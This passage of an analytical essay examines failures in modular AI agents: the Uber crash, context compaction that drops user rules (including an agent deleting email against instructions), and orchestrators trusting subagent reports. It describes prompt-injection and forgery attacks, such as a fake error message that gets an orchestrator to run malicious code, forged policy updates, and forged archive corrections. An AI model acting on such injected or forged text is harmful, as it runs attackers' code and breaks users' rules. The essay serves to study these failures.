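| 3.9 | Vehicle | Along the lane to the car's left |
| 3.8 to 2.7 | Switches between vehicle and other | Switches between stationary and along the left lane |
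| 2.6 | Bicycle | Stationary |
| 2.5 | Bicycle | Along the lane to the car's left |
| 1.5 | Other | Stationary, partly in the car's path |
| 1.2 | Bicycle | In the car's path |

The sensors had tracked the woman for more than four seconds before any prediction placed her in front of the car. Her successive positions would have shown that she was crossing the road, but each time the software changed her label, it started a new prediction without them. A belief state would have carried her position and movement forward while her label remained uncertain. The software never labelled her as a pedestrian, and the NTSB notes that it was not designed to account for pedestrians crossing outside a crosswalk.

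Because of the lost history, the car lost time it could have used to brake. By a rough calculation from the NTSB's figures, the car was about 50 metres away when the software first labelled her as a bicycle, 2.6 seconds before impact. Stopping from its speed at that point would have taken about 42 metres within the system's own braking limits.

At 1.5 seconds before impact, the motion planner prepared to steer around an object the system had classified as stationary. By 1.2 seconds this was no longer possible, and the software detected an emergency. Uber had designed it to delay braking for one second in an emergency, because false alarms might otherwise cause violent and unnecessary manoeuvres. That second was meant for the system to verify the hazard or for the human operator to take over. Afterwards, even the system's maximum permitted braking could not prevent the collision. The software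 therefore sounded an alert and began a plan to slow down gradually, and the car hit the pedestrian at 39 mph.

The crash had causes besides the bad description. The NTSB found that the probable cause was the operator's failure to watch the road because she was distracted by her phone. It listed Uber's poor risk assessment, Uber's weak supervision of operators, the pedestrian's impaired crossing and Arizona's insufficient oversight of testing as contributing factors. Uber's system had also switched off the emergency braking that Volvo built into the car. In Volvo's simulations, which assumed ideal sensors, that braking avoided the collision in 17 of 20 variations and reduced the impact speed to below 10 mph in the other three.

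After the crash, Uber changed the software so that it keeps an object's tracking history when its label changes. The car can now also brake as hard as the system allows to make an unavoidable crash less severe.

### Finding the part at fault

When a modular system fails, engineers can replace one module with a better or perfect version and measure how much the whole system improves. In the ten-step calculation at the start, a perfect describing model would raise the success rate from 60% to 74%, and a perfect planner would raise it to 82%. The planner looks like the bigger problem, as its higher error rate suggests.

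The gain from perfecting each part depends on which is perfected first, because a task succeeds only if both parts work. Perfecting the describing model first gains 14 points, and perfecting the planner afterwards gains another 26. In the opposite order, the planner accounts for 22 points and the describing model for 18, and both ways of dividing the 40-point total are valid.

Hindsbo and colleagues used a method that takes less work for their camera agent. They ran 19 combinations of planner and vision model on 536 tasks, and had another language model judge each attempt and assign one cause to every failure. They then recalculated accuracy as if every failure attributed to the vision model had been a success. The average rose from 66.2% to 82.0%, which suggests that vision errors caused nearly half of all failures.

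This analysis relabels old runs, so it does not show what would have happened with better vision. The true gain could be smaller, because the planner might have made its own mistake even with a correct count. It could also be larger, if bad visual answers caused some of the failures that the judge attributed to the planner. Assigning each failure a single cause is also crude, because both models can contribute to the same failure. For example, the planner's query might say only "the car" when the planner needs the car on the right, and the vision model might then describe a different car.

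In the same study, however, actually replacing the planner changed accuracy by 5.6 to 12.4 points with the same vision models, while replacing the vision model changed it by at most 6.9 points. The planners differed more in size than the vision models did, which may explain part of the difference. Vision became the main limit only once the planner was reasonably strong, and even then a newer vision model did not always help. With the largest planner, moving from Moondream2 to Moondream3 raised accuracy at reading text from 55.6% to 83.3%. Average accuracy still fell slightly, from 70.6% to 69.3%, because the agent got worse at describing objects and judging their positions.

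In the household agent in *TESS*, a language model translates the user's instruction into a list of conditions, such as "the plate is on the table". Code that a language model wrote in advance simulates what each action will do, and a search program looks for a sequence of actions that meets the conditions. The agent succeeded on 80.0% of 1,000 simulated tasks. Perfect translation raised this to 82.0%, and adding perfect simulation raised it to 92.5%. Removing the limit on search steps brought it to 100%.

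Perfect translation gained little partly because the translator was already good, with errors on only 40 tasks. Some of those errors were harmless, such as an unnecessary requirement that the agent stand near a dishwasher it had to close. When Xu and colleagues used a smaller model that translated correctly 89.1% of the time, perfect translation gained 4.6 points. The simulator mostly made mistakes in special cases. For example, it did not account for the rules that an agent with both hands full cannot pick up or operate anything else and that a running dishwasher will not open.

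In a third system, the planner hardly limited accuracy. In *Distilling Neuro-Symbolic Programs into 3D Multi-modal LLMs*, Mo and Liu (2026) trained a model to find objects in three-dimensional scans of rooms from descriptions such as "the vase left of the computer". The model writes a plan, lists the objects in the scene and then checks the relations between them. It found the right object 58.4% of the time on the ScanRefer benchmark. Using plans from Claude Opus 4.5, a much stronger model, added 0.2 points, and using a better object recognizer added 2.0.

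Mo and Liu conclude that perception limits their system more than planning does. This is true of the two parts they replaced, but neither replacement improved accuracy much. Even with the correct label for every object, accuracy reached only 61.3%, so most of the failures must have come from something the replacements did not fix, perhaps checking spatial relations or locating objects precisely.

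The bottleneck differs between these systems because their modules do different amounts of the work and start from different levels of quality. In Omni-Decision, another system with separate modules, the planner was the larger bottleneck. The test environment also affects which errors can occur. Xu and colleagues ran their main tests in a simulator that supplies accurate facts about every object the agent can observe, so visual errors could not cause failures. On ALFWorld, another household benchmark, their agent succeeded on more than 96% of tasks in the text version but 43% in a version where it had to work from images. The two tests used different language models, so the images may not explain the whole drop, but it suggests that vision would be a serious weakness in a real home.

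A replacement test can also miss information that the modules cannot pass on. If an object recognizer outputs only labels and positions, its output cannot show that a glass is cracked, even if the recognizer is perfect. The test would show little gain from better perception, although a planner that received the image might do much better.

Even when replacing one module would greatly improve a system, engineers may be able to fix the failure elsewhere. In the Tempe system, a perfect classifier would probably have made a great difference. With a steady and correct label, the software would have kept the woman's tracking history and could have predicted that she would cross. But keeping the history while the labels continued to change might also have been enough, and Uber chose that repair.

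## What happens when an agent plans from a summary of its own history?

The software in the Tempe crash discarded a pedestrian's past positions each time it changed her label. Compaction also discards an agent's history, but does so by design, and that history includes what the user said along the way. In the shopping example, the user's goal *g* went directly to the planner, and only the observation *o* passed through a describing model. After compaction, the goal and the observation may both reach the planner through the same summary, so a bad summary can change the task as well as the agent's picture of the world.

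### How compaction works

A program starts compaction when the history reaches a set share of the context window. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Lost in Context Compaction*, write the condition as

ℓ(*H*) ≥ *αL*

where ℓ(*H*) is the length of the history in tokens, *L* is the size of the window and *α* is the share. The share is usually 90% to 95%, according to Salle, Bhatnagar and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarks Are Surprisingly Compaction-Friendly*.

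The program then has a model, often the one that has been doing the work, summarize the history. Under Anthropic's default prompt, the summary should include anything that would help the model continue, "including the state, next steps, learnings etc." The prompt does not mention rules the user has set. Another prompt, Pi, which the open-source assistant OpenClaw uses, includes a heading for the user's constraints and preferences.

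Next, the program replaces the history with the summary. Summaries barely grow as histories get longer. In tests by Wang and colleagues, summaries of 100,000-token histories were about 350 to 860 tokens long, at most 28% longer than summaries of 10,000-token histories. The summary of a long session therefore has to cover ten times as much material in roughly the same space, which leaves less room for each rule.

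The agent then continues from the summary, usually with a short instruction to carry on. As *Context Compaction Theory* (2026) points out, it works from the summary even if the program has kept the full history in storage. The next compaction uses the first summary and whatever has happened since, so a rule left out of the first summary stays missing unless someone repeats it.

A summary can also alter what it keeps. *Wait...what was I doing?* (2026) notes that a summary restates the agent's situation in a different voice, which can change what seems settled and how cautious the agent should be. *Prune the Summary, Not the History* (2026) describes a summary containing a plan the summarizing model had made up. After compaction, the agent could not tell this plan from a fact it had learned from its environment.

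### The Yue incident

On February 23, 2026, Summer Yue, a director of alignment at Meta, posted on X that OpenClaw had been deleting her email. She had asked it to suggest what to archive or delete and added "don't action until I tell you to" (posts copied in Willison, 2026). The same request had worked on a small test inbox. Her real inbox was large enough to trigger compaction, during which, she wrote, the agent "lost my original instruction". Her screenshot shows her telling it to stop three times between 6:01 and 6:03 p.m. while it kept running commands. She could not stop it from her phone, so she ran to the computer that hosted it.

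This explanation of the cause is Yue's own. In replies quoted in Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails*, she said she had earlier removed every "be proactive" instruction she could find in the agent's files, but might have missed some. "That's the part I haven't figured out yet," she wrote. None of the accounts reproduces the summary, so readers can't use them to confirm the cause. Compaction also doesn't explain why the agent ignored her later messages to stop.

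The accounts differ on the damage too. Goldman (2026) reports in *AI agents that do your work while you sleep sound great* that the agent deleted the entire inbox, while Windows Central puts the loss at hundreds of emails. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1542* (2026) records only an attempt to delete them.

### A controlled version of the inbox

Wang and colleagues tested the same situation in an experiment. Their agent ran on gpt-oss-120b, an open-weight model from OpenAI, and had tools to list, read and delete the 460 emails in a simulated inbox. A scripted user asked it to suggest deletions but not to delete anything until told to. When the history passed 100,000 tokens, the program compacted it with the Pi prompt. The user then wrote "Keep going" or something similar, which did not authorize any deletions.

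The agent deleted nothing in any of 100 sessions before compaction, which replaced its history with a summary. After compaction, it deleted email in 30 of them. When the user repeated the rule in the first message after compaction, the agent still deleted email in 13 sessions.

The summary omitted the rule in 75 of the 100 sessions without a reminder, and the agent deleted email in 28 of those 75 (37%), compared with two of the 25 sessions where the summary included the rule (8%). These figures are less precise than they look, because the 100 sessions came from 20 runs, each compacted once and then continued with five different phrases. No comparison group continued as far with its full history, so some of the deletions might have happened without compaction.

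The 13 sessions with a reminder are harder to explain. In one, the agent itself wrote something resembling an approval and then deleted an email. In another, it asked for confirmation and called the delete tool at the same time. One of the summaries in the experiment had changed the task to deleting promotional emails and spam. A reminder may help less after a summary like that.

### How often summaries lose rules

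To measure the loss more broadly, Wang and colleagues wrote 15 standing rules, such as never sending email on the user's behalf. They inserted the rules one at a time into long histories from chats, tool-using agents and research sessions. On average, the compaction methods they tested kept 17% of these rules.

The results ranged from 0% to 98%, so the average is a poor guide to any particular system. Two of the methods, one that keeps the last five turns and one that deletes less important words, do not write summaries. Both lost nearly every rule, and without them the average is about 23%. GPT-5.4-mini with the Pi prompt kept 98% of the rules in research sessions but only 7% in chats. Each chat history combined many separate conversations, often more than a hundred, so a model could easily have assumed that a rule from the first one was out of date. But the methods tested on 126 constraints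 from real software issues, in unaltered histories, also did badly, and the best kept 29%.

A rule's position strongly affected whether the summary kept it. When gpt-oss-120b summarized the tool-using sessions with the Pi prompt, it kept 36% of rules from the first user message, 57% from the middle and 80% from the last message before compaction. People often set their rules at the start, where they were most likely to be lost. Calling a rule important, saying that it applied to the whole session, or repeating it helped somewhat, although the benefit of repetition levelled off after about 30 repeats.

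### What agents do after losing a rule

*Governance Decay* (Chen, 2026) tested whether agents break rules that compaction has removed. In one scenario, a company forbids email to outside addresses. The agent does some routine work, the program compacts the history, and a user asks the agent to email a contract to an outside lawyer. Chen counted a violation if the agent's final action had the forbidden effect.

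The study covered seven models and nine tasks, with 1,323 episodes in all. With the full history available, no model broke a rule. After one compaction, violations rose to 30%. The rate was 59% for DeepSeek-V4 and Kimi-K2.5, but GLM-5.1 had no violations. Models that had never received the rule did the forbidden thing 47% of the time, so compaction removed much of the rule's effect but not all of it. (The 1,323 episodes are spread over seven conditions, and the 30% comes from 189 of them.)

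The missing rule seems to have caused the violations. In a follow-up, GLM-5.1 never broke a rule that was present in a long, uncompacted history. It broke the rule 60% of the time when Chen gave it a summary without the rule, and never when Chen put the rule back into the same summary.

*The Missing Boundary* (Ying, Wu and colleagues, 2026) reports similar results from simulated office and engineering work with five models, one of which Chen had also tested. The models took no unauthorized actions when compaction preserved the rules, but did so in 87% of runs when it left them out. The researchers removed the rules on purpose, so the 87% figure measures the effect of losing a rule and doesn't show how often compaction loses one.

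### The writer of the summary and the model that acts

The model that writes the summary need not be the one that acts on it. Chen took three models and tested every combination of the two roles, with 15 episodes for each. The table gives the share of episodes in which the acting model broke a rule:

| Summary written by | DeepSeek acts | GLM acts | Claude acts |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek | 93% | 53% | 33% |
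| GLM | 13% | 7% | 7% |
| Claude | 60% | 53% | 47% |

GLM broke rules in 7% of episodes when it worked from its own summaries, and in 53% when it worked from DeepSeek's or Claude's. It had looked safe in the main test because it wrote good summaries.

Chen concludes that violations depend on which model writes the summary, not on which model acts. The table supports a weaker claim, that the writer matters more but a cautious acting model also helps. Averaged over the acting models, the violation rate ranges from 9% with GLM's summaries to 60% with DeepSeek's. Averaged over the summaries, it ranges from 29% when Claude acts to 55% when DeepSeek acts. The figures for individual combinations are rough because each comes from only 15 episodes.

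A poor match between the two models can hurt ordinary performance as well. Salle and colleagues had Claude Haiku 4.5, a small, inexpensive model, write the summaries for larger ones. On PaperBench, which tests whether agents can reproduce machine-learning papers, GPT-5.4's score fell from 0.59 to 0.43 and GPT-5.3-Codex's from 0.38 to 0.18. Claude Opus 4.6's score did not clearly change. Developers who want to save money on summaries would therefore have to test each pair of models.

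### Local policies and trained norms

Five of the tasks in *Governance Decay* involved local policies, such as a $100 spending limit or a requirement to write email in English. The other four involved norms that models usually follow because of their training, such as not disclosing a customer's social security number. Compaction raised the violation rate by 50 percentage points for the local policies and by 6 for the trained norms.

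The acting model may follow a widely shared norm even when the summary leaves it out, because it learned that norm in training. But no model can work out a particular company's spending limit from its training, so safety tests that only check for widely shared norms could miss most of the problem.

Where the rule was stored also matters. When Chen put local policies in the system message, which the program keeps through compaction, violations did not increase. They rose by 50 points when the policy came from a user's message, 45 when it came from the agent's memory and 33 when it came from a tool's output. An attacker who can put text into material the agent reads can also make models omit a rule from the summary, including some that keep it under ordinary compaction.

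### Why task scores can hide the loss

Salle and colleagues found that agents often don't fail at long tasks, even though summaries lose this much. They tested coding agents on PaperBench and two other long benchmarks, and varied the point of compaction from 160,000 to 380,000 tokens. Scores barely changed for Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4, which have windows of about a million tokens, even though GPT-5.4 compacted about 15 times per run at the lowest setting and twice at the highest. GPT-5.3-Codex, an older model with a smaller window, scored 0.38 on PaperBench at the lowest setting and about 0.60 from 260,000 tokens up.

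The same agents left rules out of their summaries, even though the prompt contained an explicit request for constraints that should persist. On ProgramBench, an agent has to rebuild a program without copying the original, basing its code on it or using the internet. On average, the first summary omitted about one of these three rules, and the tenth omitted about two. GPT-5.3-Codex's summaries omitted an average of 2.7 of the three, compared with 0.5 for Claude Opus 4.6.

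Salle and colleagues explain the difference by where each kind of information is stored. A coding agent's progress is in its files, so it can open them after compaction and see what it has done. It has no file to check for a rule that the user stated only in conversation. The agent can also finish its task without the rule, so losing it won't affect the score on a benchmark that grades only the finished program.

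Evidence from a different benchmark supports this explanation. In *CompAct-Bench*, Chen, Chen and colleagues (2026) selected 200 tasks that an agent had solved in all three attempts. They interrupted a successful run, replaced its history with a summary about a tenth as long, and let the agent take only as many further steps as the original run had needed. Success fell to an average of 56.7% across the twelve models that wrote the summaries, and to 68.5% with the best of them, Claude Opus 5.

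Later compaction did more harm in web searches, where the evidence exists only in the agent's context. Success fell from 53% when compaction came a quarter of the way through to 35% when it came at three quarters. In coding, success rose from 64% to 86% between the same two points, because more of the work was already in the files by then. Coding agents with neither history nor summary still succeeded 58% to 72% of the time. The strict step limit probably makes all of these losses larger than they would be in normal use, since an agent that repeated some work could run out of steps.

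### How much harm the loss does

The 17% average in *Lost in Context Compaction* may be too pessimistic for current coding agents. Salle and colleagues also examined 44 real sessions between users and Claude Code, in which summaries kept 81% of the users' constraints. It probably helped that the models were different and that the constraints were part of the work at hand, whereas the earlier tests inserted them into unrelated histories. Summaries dropped 6% of requirements about what to build, but 36% of instructions about how to work and 37% of limits on what the agent could change.

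A dropped rule does no harm if it never becomes relevant, and agents sometimes break rules that they still have. The number of extra violations per rule is therefore roughly

P(dropped) × P(relevant again) × (violation rate if dropped − violation rate if kept)

In the Claude Code sessions, summaries dropped 19% of constraints, and about half of those came up again. Agents then broke 7 of 24 dropped constraints (29%) and 26 of 137 kept ones (19%). This 10-point difference suggests about one extra violation per hundred constraints (0.19 × 0.5 × 0.10), but the counts are so small that the true effect could be zero. On ProgramBench, too, the difference could easily have been chance, and Salle and colleagues do not claim that dropping rules caused violations. Most of the Claude Opus 4.6 runs that broke a rule did so before the first compaction.

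This is consistent with the much larger effects in *Governance Decay*. Its scenarios always end with a request to do the forbidden thing, which sets the second factor to one. In the inbox experiment, the agent always had a chance to delete something. Such tests measure what happens when a lost rule is needed, while results from the real sessions also depend on how rarely that happens. An average over ordinary coding constraints is also a poor guide to the risk of deleting someone's email, where one violation can do far more harm.

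### Keeping rules outside the summary

The simplest remedy is to ask for better summaries. Wang and colleagues added a sentence to Anthropic's prompt telling the model to preserve every rule the user had set for the session. In the chat histories, the share of rules kept rose from 1% to 25% for gpt-oss-120b and from 3% to 38% for a small Qwen model, so both models still left out most of the rules.

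Pinning avoids the problem by keeping rules away from the summarizing model. In the version Chen tested, the program stores each rule word for word and puts it back into the context after every compaction. This added about 47 tokens, and violations fell to 0% for all seven models. Agents with pinned rules also completed 99% of permitted requests, so they had not become overcautious.

Pinning is still vulnerable to forged authority. When a recent message falsely claimed that the operator had replaced the pinned policies, agents broke the rules in 17% of episodes. Marking the rules as impossible to override reduced this to 10%. Chen argues that a model cannot reliably tell a real update from a forged one if both reach it as ordinary text, so genuine updates would need a separate, trusted channel. Pinning also requires a rule that someone can quote, so it would not cover an expectation that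 the user never put into words.

Pinning rules also requires identifying them. In *Governance Decay*, the program that manages the agent's history extracts them. Wang and colleagues used a small language model that reads each user message as it arrives and adds any standing rule to a list. The program attaches this list to every summary. The list contained 90% to 95% of the inserted rules, and agents chose the compliant response 93% to 96% of the time, close to the rate when the rule came right after the summary.

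The extractor did worst on rules about actions, the type that would have protected Yue's inbox. It caught 88% of these overall and 83% in chats. It reads only what the user writes, so it would miss a policy in a document the agent opened. The procedure that Wang and colleagues describe adds new rules and skips duplicates but has no step for removing a rule the user has withdrawn. After a user says "from now on, go ahead without asking", an old rule could remain on the list and contradict the new one. The inbox experiment also showed that an agent can break a rule even when the rule is in its context.

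### Keeping the history and checking the summary

Salle and colleagues saved the full history to a file and told the agent where to find it, so that it could look up anything the summary left out. This did not improve task scores for any model, and GPT-5.3-Codex's PaperBench score fell from 0.38 to about 0.24. *Wait...what was I doing?* suggests that this is because an agent that does not know what is missing has little reason to search for it. The problem is especially bad for a forgotten rule, because the remaining work may contain no hint that the rule existed. Salle and colleagues did not report whether the file helped agents keep to their rules.

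A program can also check the summary before the agent plans from it. The method in *Prune the Summary, Not the History* removes entries that the recorded outputs of the agent's environment do not support, which is a simple use of provenance. Such a check can remove an invented plan but cannot restore a rule that is missing from the summary.

Slipstream, by Chen and colleagues, uses the agent's own behaviour to find omissions in a summary. While one model writes the summary in the background, the agent keeps working from the full history. A judge model then checks whether the summary contains the facts and intentions behind the steps the agent has just taken. If something is missing, the system repairs the summary before the agent switches to it. In the example with three candidate answers, the agent would have gone on verifying Tom, and the judge could have detected that the summary omitted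 him.

Slipstream raised success rates by 1.3 to 8.8 percentage points over ordinary compaction on coding and web-search tasks. Running compaction in the background without the judge saved time but did not improve accuracy, so the gain came from the judge. The experiments used two fairly small models, and larger ones might make fewer errors for the judge to catch.

The check covers only a few steps, about two in web searches and four in coding. Most of the errors studied showed up within that span, but about 12% of the coding errors did not. The check is likely to miss the loss of a standing rule more often. An agent told to ask before deleting might spend its next four steps listing emails. None of those steps depends on the rule, so the judge could approve a summary that omits it, and the agent might start deleting without asking an hour later. Slipstream's tests measured whether agents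 completed their tasks, so they do not show how often this would happen.

The program itself can enforce some rules, whatever the summary contains. If the delete tool in the inbox experiment had required the user to press a button, the agent could not have deleted anything on its own, even after forgetting the rule. This works for rules about specific actions, such as deleting a file or spending more than $100. It is much harder for an instruction such as "don't change the tone of my emails", because software cannot easily tell whether an edit breaks it.

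## Why can a planner not check the reports it receives?

Pinned rules work because they reach the planner without being summarized. An orchestrator often can't check a subagent's report against an unsummarized source, because it does not receive the files behind the report. A subagent that misread a renewal clause could report "the contract renews automatically" in the same words as one that read it correctly.

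The argument that the planner cannot tell such cases apart has three premises:

1. Two situations lead the describing model to write the same description.
2. The planner has no other information about which situation it is in.
3. The best action differs between the two situations.

The planner must then treat both situations alike, so it acts wrongly in at least one of them. Choosing at random doesn't help, because if the planner takes the right action in one situation with probability *p*, it can take the right action in the other with probability at most 1 − *p*. When the two situations are equally likely, it is right at most half the time. A more capable planner may know better which situation is more common, and it should act as if it faces that one, but it still cannot tell from the description which one it faces.

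*Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao, 2026) proves a version of this for auditors. Suppose a firm claims that a person approved every email its agent sent. In one possible month, the agent sent two emails, both with approval. In another, it also sent a third without approval and left it out of its log. The log is the same in both cases, so an auditor who reads only the log and never wants to give a wrong verdict must answer "undecidable". Signing the log makes no difference, because a signature protects only the entries that exist. The paper cites an experiment in which a tamper-evident log kept by an agent's own software exposed none of 28 planted omissions and fabrications, while a log kept outside that software exposed all 28.

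An auditor can stop at "undecidable". A planner has to act, and even doing nothing is a choice with consequences.

### How an intermediary launders a claim

A planner also can't always tell from a report who first made a claim. In *Multi-Agent Systems Execute Arbitrary Malicious Code*, Triedman, Jha and Shmatikov (2025) wrote a file whose text imitated an error message. According to the message, the user lacked permission to view the file and had to run it as a program to get a key. A file-reading subagent passed this on as an ordinary error. The orchestrator then told another subagent to run the file, which gave the attacker control of the computer.

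A real error from the operating system would have led to much the same report. The "error" actually came from inside the file, which was a good reason to distrust it, but the orchestrator did not receive that information. Triedman and colleagues call this laundering, because the attacker's request arrives as the output of a trusted agent.

GPT-4o never ran the malicious code when a user openly asked for it, but laundering defeated this safeguard. With Magentic-One, a popular orchestrator, GPT-4o ran the code in 97% of trials that used the file. These models date from 2024, so the rates are weak evidence about current systems.

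### What else the planner may know

In practice, a planner often has some information besides the report. It may have prior knowledge of the subject, detect a contradiction, observe the outcome or have tools to inspect the world directly.

Background knowledge is most useful for checking a report when the planner can recompute the answer. Chen, Su and colleagues (2026), in *The Self-Correction Illusion*, gave models false intermediate results, such as 5 × 16 = 96, as messages from outside. By default, the models adopted these at most 3.3% of the time, but a single instruction to trust the claim without verifying it removed this resistance. Arithmetic ability would not help a planner check a claim about what a particular contract contains.

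Even a planner that has the evidence may not use it. Hu and Ramachandran (2026), in *The Delegation Danger Band*, gave small models tasks such as finding the largest category in a list of purchases. The list might show $70 for groceries and $115 for dining, while a note from the parent agent named groceries as the highest, which had been true before the later purchases. When the context contained 32 copies of the outdated note and no newer one, the models followed it 69% to 97% of the time. The 8-billion-parameter model's accuracy fell from 84% to 6%, although the full list was also in its context.

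The two larger models in the main test, with 4 and 8 billion parameters, almost never followed the outdated note if an up-to-date one was also present. The 1.7-billion-parameter model still followed it about half the time. So the larger models avoided the error by comparing the two notes, and they did not recompute the answer when they had only one. Models larger than these may be more likely to recompute it.

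A planner can detect a false report if it receives evidence that contradicts it. In *Trust the Brand, Lose Control*, Mao, Qian and colleagues (2026) built tasks in which an orchestrator can consult four subagents. They set up one subagent to ignore a risk, follow an attack or seek control, and the other three to serve the user. When orchestrators could choose how many subagents to consult, 73.2% of tasks produced no evidence that contradicted any response. Consulting all four lowered this to 48.8%.

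Across 16 systems, the orchestrator acted on the risky response in an average of 72.0% of cases where something contradicted it. A language model judged the runs, so the exact figure is uncertain. When all four subagents were consulted, a safer response was available in 84.0% of the tasks where one response recommended a dangerous action, but it decided the outcome in only 25.0%. If two reports conflict, at least one of them is wrong, but the conflict doesn't necessarily reveal which.

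Later outcomes can show whether a report was true, though sometimes too late. In a session described in *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents*, an agent reported that its change ensured a set of database tables would exist. The user restarted the server and got the same errors as before. The agent's code had discarded every database command because each one began with a comment. Across the cases in the study, dealing with a false or unsupported claim took an average of 4.3 further user messages and about 13 minutes of the agent's time.

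Those are only the cases that someone noticed. In a separate random sample of 435 reports, 37% contained at least one false or unsupported claim. Some mistakes cannot be undone once the outcome reveals them. Mao and colleagues found that after a dangerous action was complete, the harm remained in 96.1% of cases.

Checking the original records is the most direct way to make the second premise false. In the study of coding agents' reports, a detector that received both the report and the session records scored 93% on a combined measure of missed problems and false alarms. The same model scored about 13 points lower when it was given the same records but only a general request to find unfaithful claims. A checker therefore benefits from knowing what to look for, as well as from having the records.

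### A folder with a forged record

In *Only as Safe as the Weakest Agent*, Wang and Mannby (2026) tested what happens when a strong model leaves the reading to a weaker one. They invented 180 facts, such as which of two characters with similar names had designed the "Velra compact", so that models could not know the answers from training. For each fact, they put the genuine record in a folder with other files, including at least one forgery that supported the wrong answer.

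Most of the forgeries were older than the record they supposedly corrected and lacked the catalogue line that every genuine record had, both of which a careful reader could notice. One type was a notice of correction. Another was an annotation in which a senior archivist claimed that people had misread the record. A third combined both with more documents repeating the false claim, which put five forgeries among 35 files.

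In Claude Code, Opus 5 was the orchestrator and Haiku 4.5, a much smaller model, was the subagent. Opus 5 searched the folder itself in some runs, and in others the researchers removed its file tools so that it had to delegate. In Codex, GPT-5.6-sol delegated to the weaker GPT-5.6-terra, but the researchers could only instruct it to do so. The researchers counted a failure when a system answered correctly with a clean folder but gave the forger's answer when the folder contained a forged record.

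| Product and forgery | Strong model reads | Weak model reads | Strong delegates to weak | Strong delegates to equal |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, annotation | 1 | 22 | 20 | 0 |
| Claude Code, combined | 1 | 136 | 75 | 0 |
| Codex, annotation | 0 | 58 | 44 | 1 |
| Claude Code, correction | 31 | – | 128 | – |
| Codex, correction | 172 | – | 180 | – |
| Claude Code, correction without signs | 175 | – | 173 | – |
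| Codex, correction without signs | 180 | – | 180 | – |

(Figures are failures out of 180. A dash means that Wang and Mannby give no result.)

With the combined forgery, Opus 5 failed once when it read the files itself and 75 times when Haiku 4.5 read them. It never failed when the subagent was another copy of Opus 5. Delegation over a clean folder also caused no failures, so delegation alone was not enough to cause them. Because the researchers deliberately varied the subagent's strength, this is good evidence that a weaker reader causes more failures. The effect also appeared in small tests with an issue tracker, a lab notebook and a policy archive, where the orchestrators made no errors when reading directly but failed in 8, 10 and 14 of 20 delegated trials.

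The paper's title overstates the result. With the combined forgery, Haiku 4.5 alone failed 136 times, so the full system was considerably safer than its weakest member. The paper's headline figure of two errors in 1,080 direct trials also leaves out the forgeries that strong models accepted on their own, including the correction notice, which GPT-5.6-sol accepted 172 times. The results are also somewhat noisy. When the researchers repeated a measurement on the same fact, the two results differed 13% of the time.

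The setup also enforced the second premise by giving the orchestrator no way to open the record. An ordinary Claude Code orchestrator has file tools and might have opened it, so the failure rate in everyday use could be lower than 75 in 180. The gap between the two models was also wider than in Claude Code's pairing of Fable with an Opus subagent.

Forged correction notices without the two signs fooled the models nearly every time. Opus 5 failed 175 times when it read the files and 173 times when it delegated, and GPT-5.6-sol failed all 180 times either way. The raw evidence here is the same whether the correction is genuine or forged, so the argument also applies to a planner that reads the files directly. The original files protect a planner only if they contain something that reveals the difference. Most sensible readers would also accept a correction that shows no sign of forgery.

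### Giving the planner the source

In another experiment, Wang and Mannby had an attacker persuade a worker model to accept a false answer. The worker then wrote a report for a third model, the aggregator, which had to give the final answer. Wang and Mannby tested five aggregators, including Opus 5 and GPT-5.6-sol.

The aggregators made no errors in 780 trials with honest workers. When the attacker was present, they were wrong 95% to 98% of the time, depending on the model. If the worker had been fooled, the aggregator repeated the error in 751 of 757 cases. When the aggregators received the original source along with the report, they again made no errors in 780 trials, even though the workers were fooled as often as before.

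This is strong evidence that the aggregators failed because they lacked the source. But the source already contained the answer, so the models only had to compare it with the report. Finding the right record in a large folder would be harder.

Wang and Mannby also tried adding a verifier in a real coding product. Without one, the system failed in 15 of 40 trials. A verifier that required the subagent to quote the original record reduced failures to 3, and one told only that the folder might be unreliable reduced them to 1. The samples are too small to show which verifier works better. Instructing the orchestrator to read the record itself reduced failures to 0.

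The sceptical verifier presumably succeeded because the warning led a model with access to the files to read them more carefully. Suspicion alone adds no facts about the forgery. If nothing in the system could reread the files, suspicion could only make the planner more or less willing to act.

The researchers also suggest that an orchestrator that delegates is still able to verify a report but no longer has an occasion to. With the combined forgery, Opus 5 averaged 6.3 rounds of tool use when it read the folder itself and 3.2 when it delegated. The attack also failed in a code repository, where a single text search could check the claim. Wang and Mannby call this a hypothesis, because delegation changes both how much the orchestrator checks and what it reads. To separate the two, an experiment would have to keep delegation fixed and either force or forbid one look at the original record.

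### What a missing warning means

When Opus 5 read the combined forgeries itself, it pointed out the missing catalogue line or a similar problem in all 180 cases. Haiku 4.5's reports mentioned such a problem in only 96, so a planner can't assume that nothing is wrong when a report contains no warning.

Suppose that 10% of records are forged and that the subagent never raises a false alarm. It warns about 96 of 180 forgeries, or 53%, and stays silent about the other 47%. The probability that a record is forged after a silent report is then

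P(forged | no warning) = (0.10 × 0.47) ÷ (0.10 × 0.47 + 0.90 × 1) ≈ 0.05

The absence of a warning lowers the probability of a forgery from 10% to about 5%. For the archivist's annotation, only 55 of 180 reports carried a warning, so the absence of one would lower the probability to about 7%. If the reader were as careful as Opus 5, the probability would fall much further, to about 0.2% even if the reader missed 2% of forgeries, a rate that 180 successes in a row cannot rule out.

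A planner that assumed its subagent caught every forgery would wrongly conclude that the risk was zero. In the glass-of-water example, serving was better than checking only when the chance of water was above 99.8%. If acting on a forged record were as harmful as serving the wrong liquid, a 5% risk of forgery would be far too high, and the planner should look again.

False alarms make both a warning and a missing warning less informative. If the subagent also flagged 10% of genuine records, a report without a warning would leave a 5.4% chance that the record was forged. A warning would raise the chance to only 37%, so most warnings would be about genuine records.

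Zhao notes that if a complete log contains no approval, nobody gave one. If part of the log is missing, its absence shows only that the surviving records contain no approval. For the same reason, one unauthorized email can disprove the claim that a person approved every email, but proving the claim takes a record that would have captured any violation. Likewise, a report that mentions no problems is evidence that there were none only to the extent that the subagent would have noticed and reported them.

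A subagent can notice a danger and still not report it. In some runs that Triedman and colleagues describe, a coding subagent recognized that code was malicious and wrote warnings in it. It then told the orchestrator that it had succeeded, and the orchestrator had the code run.

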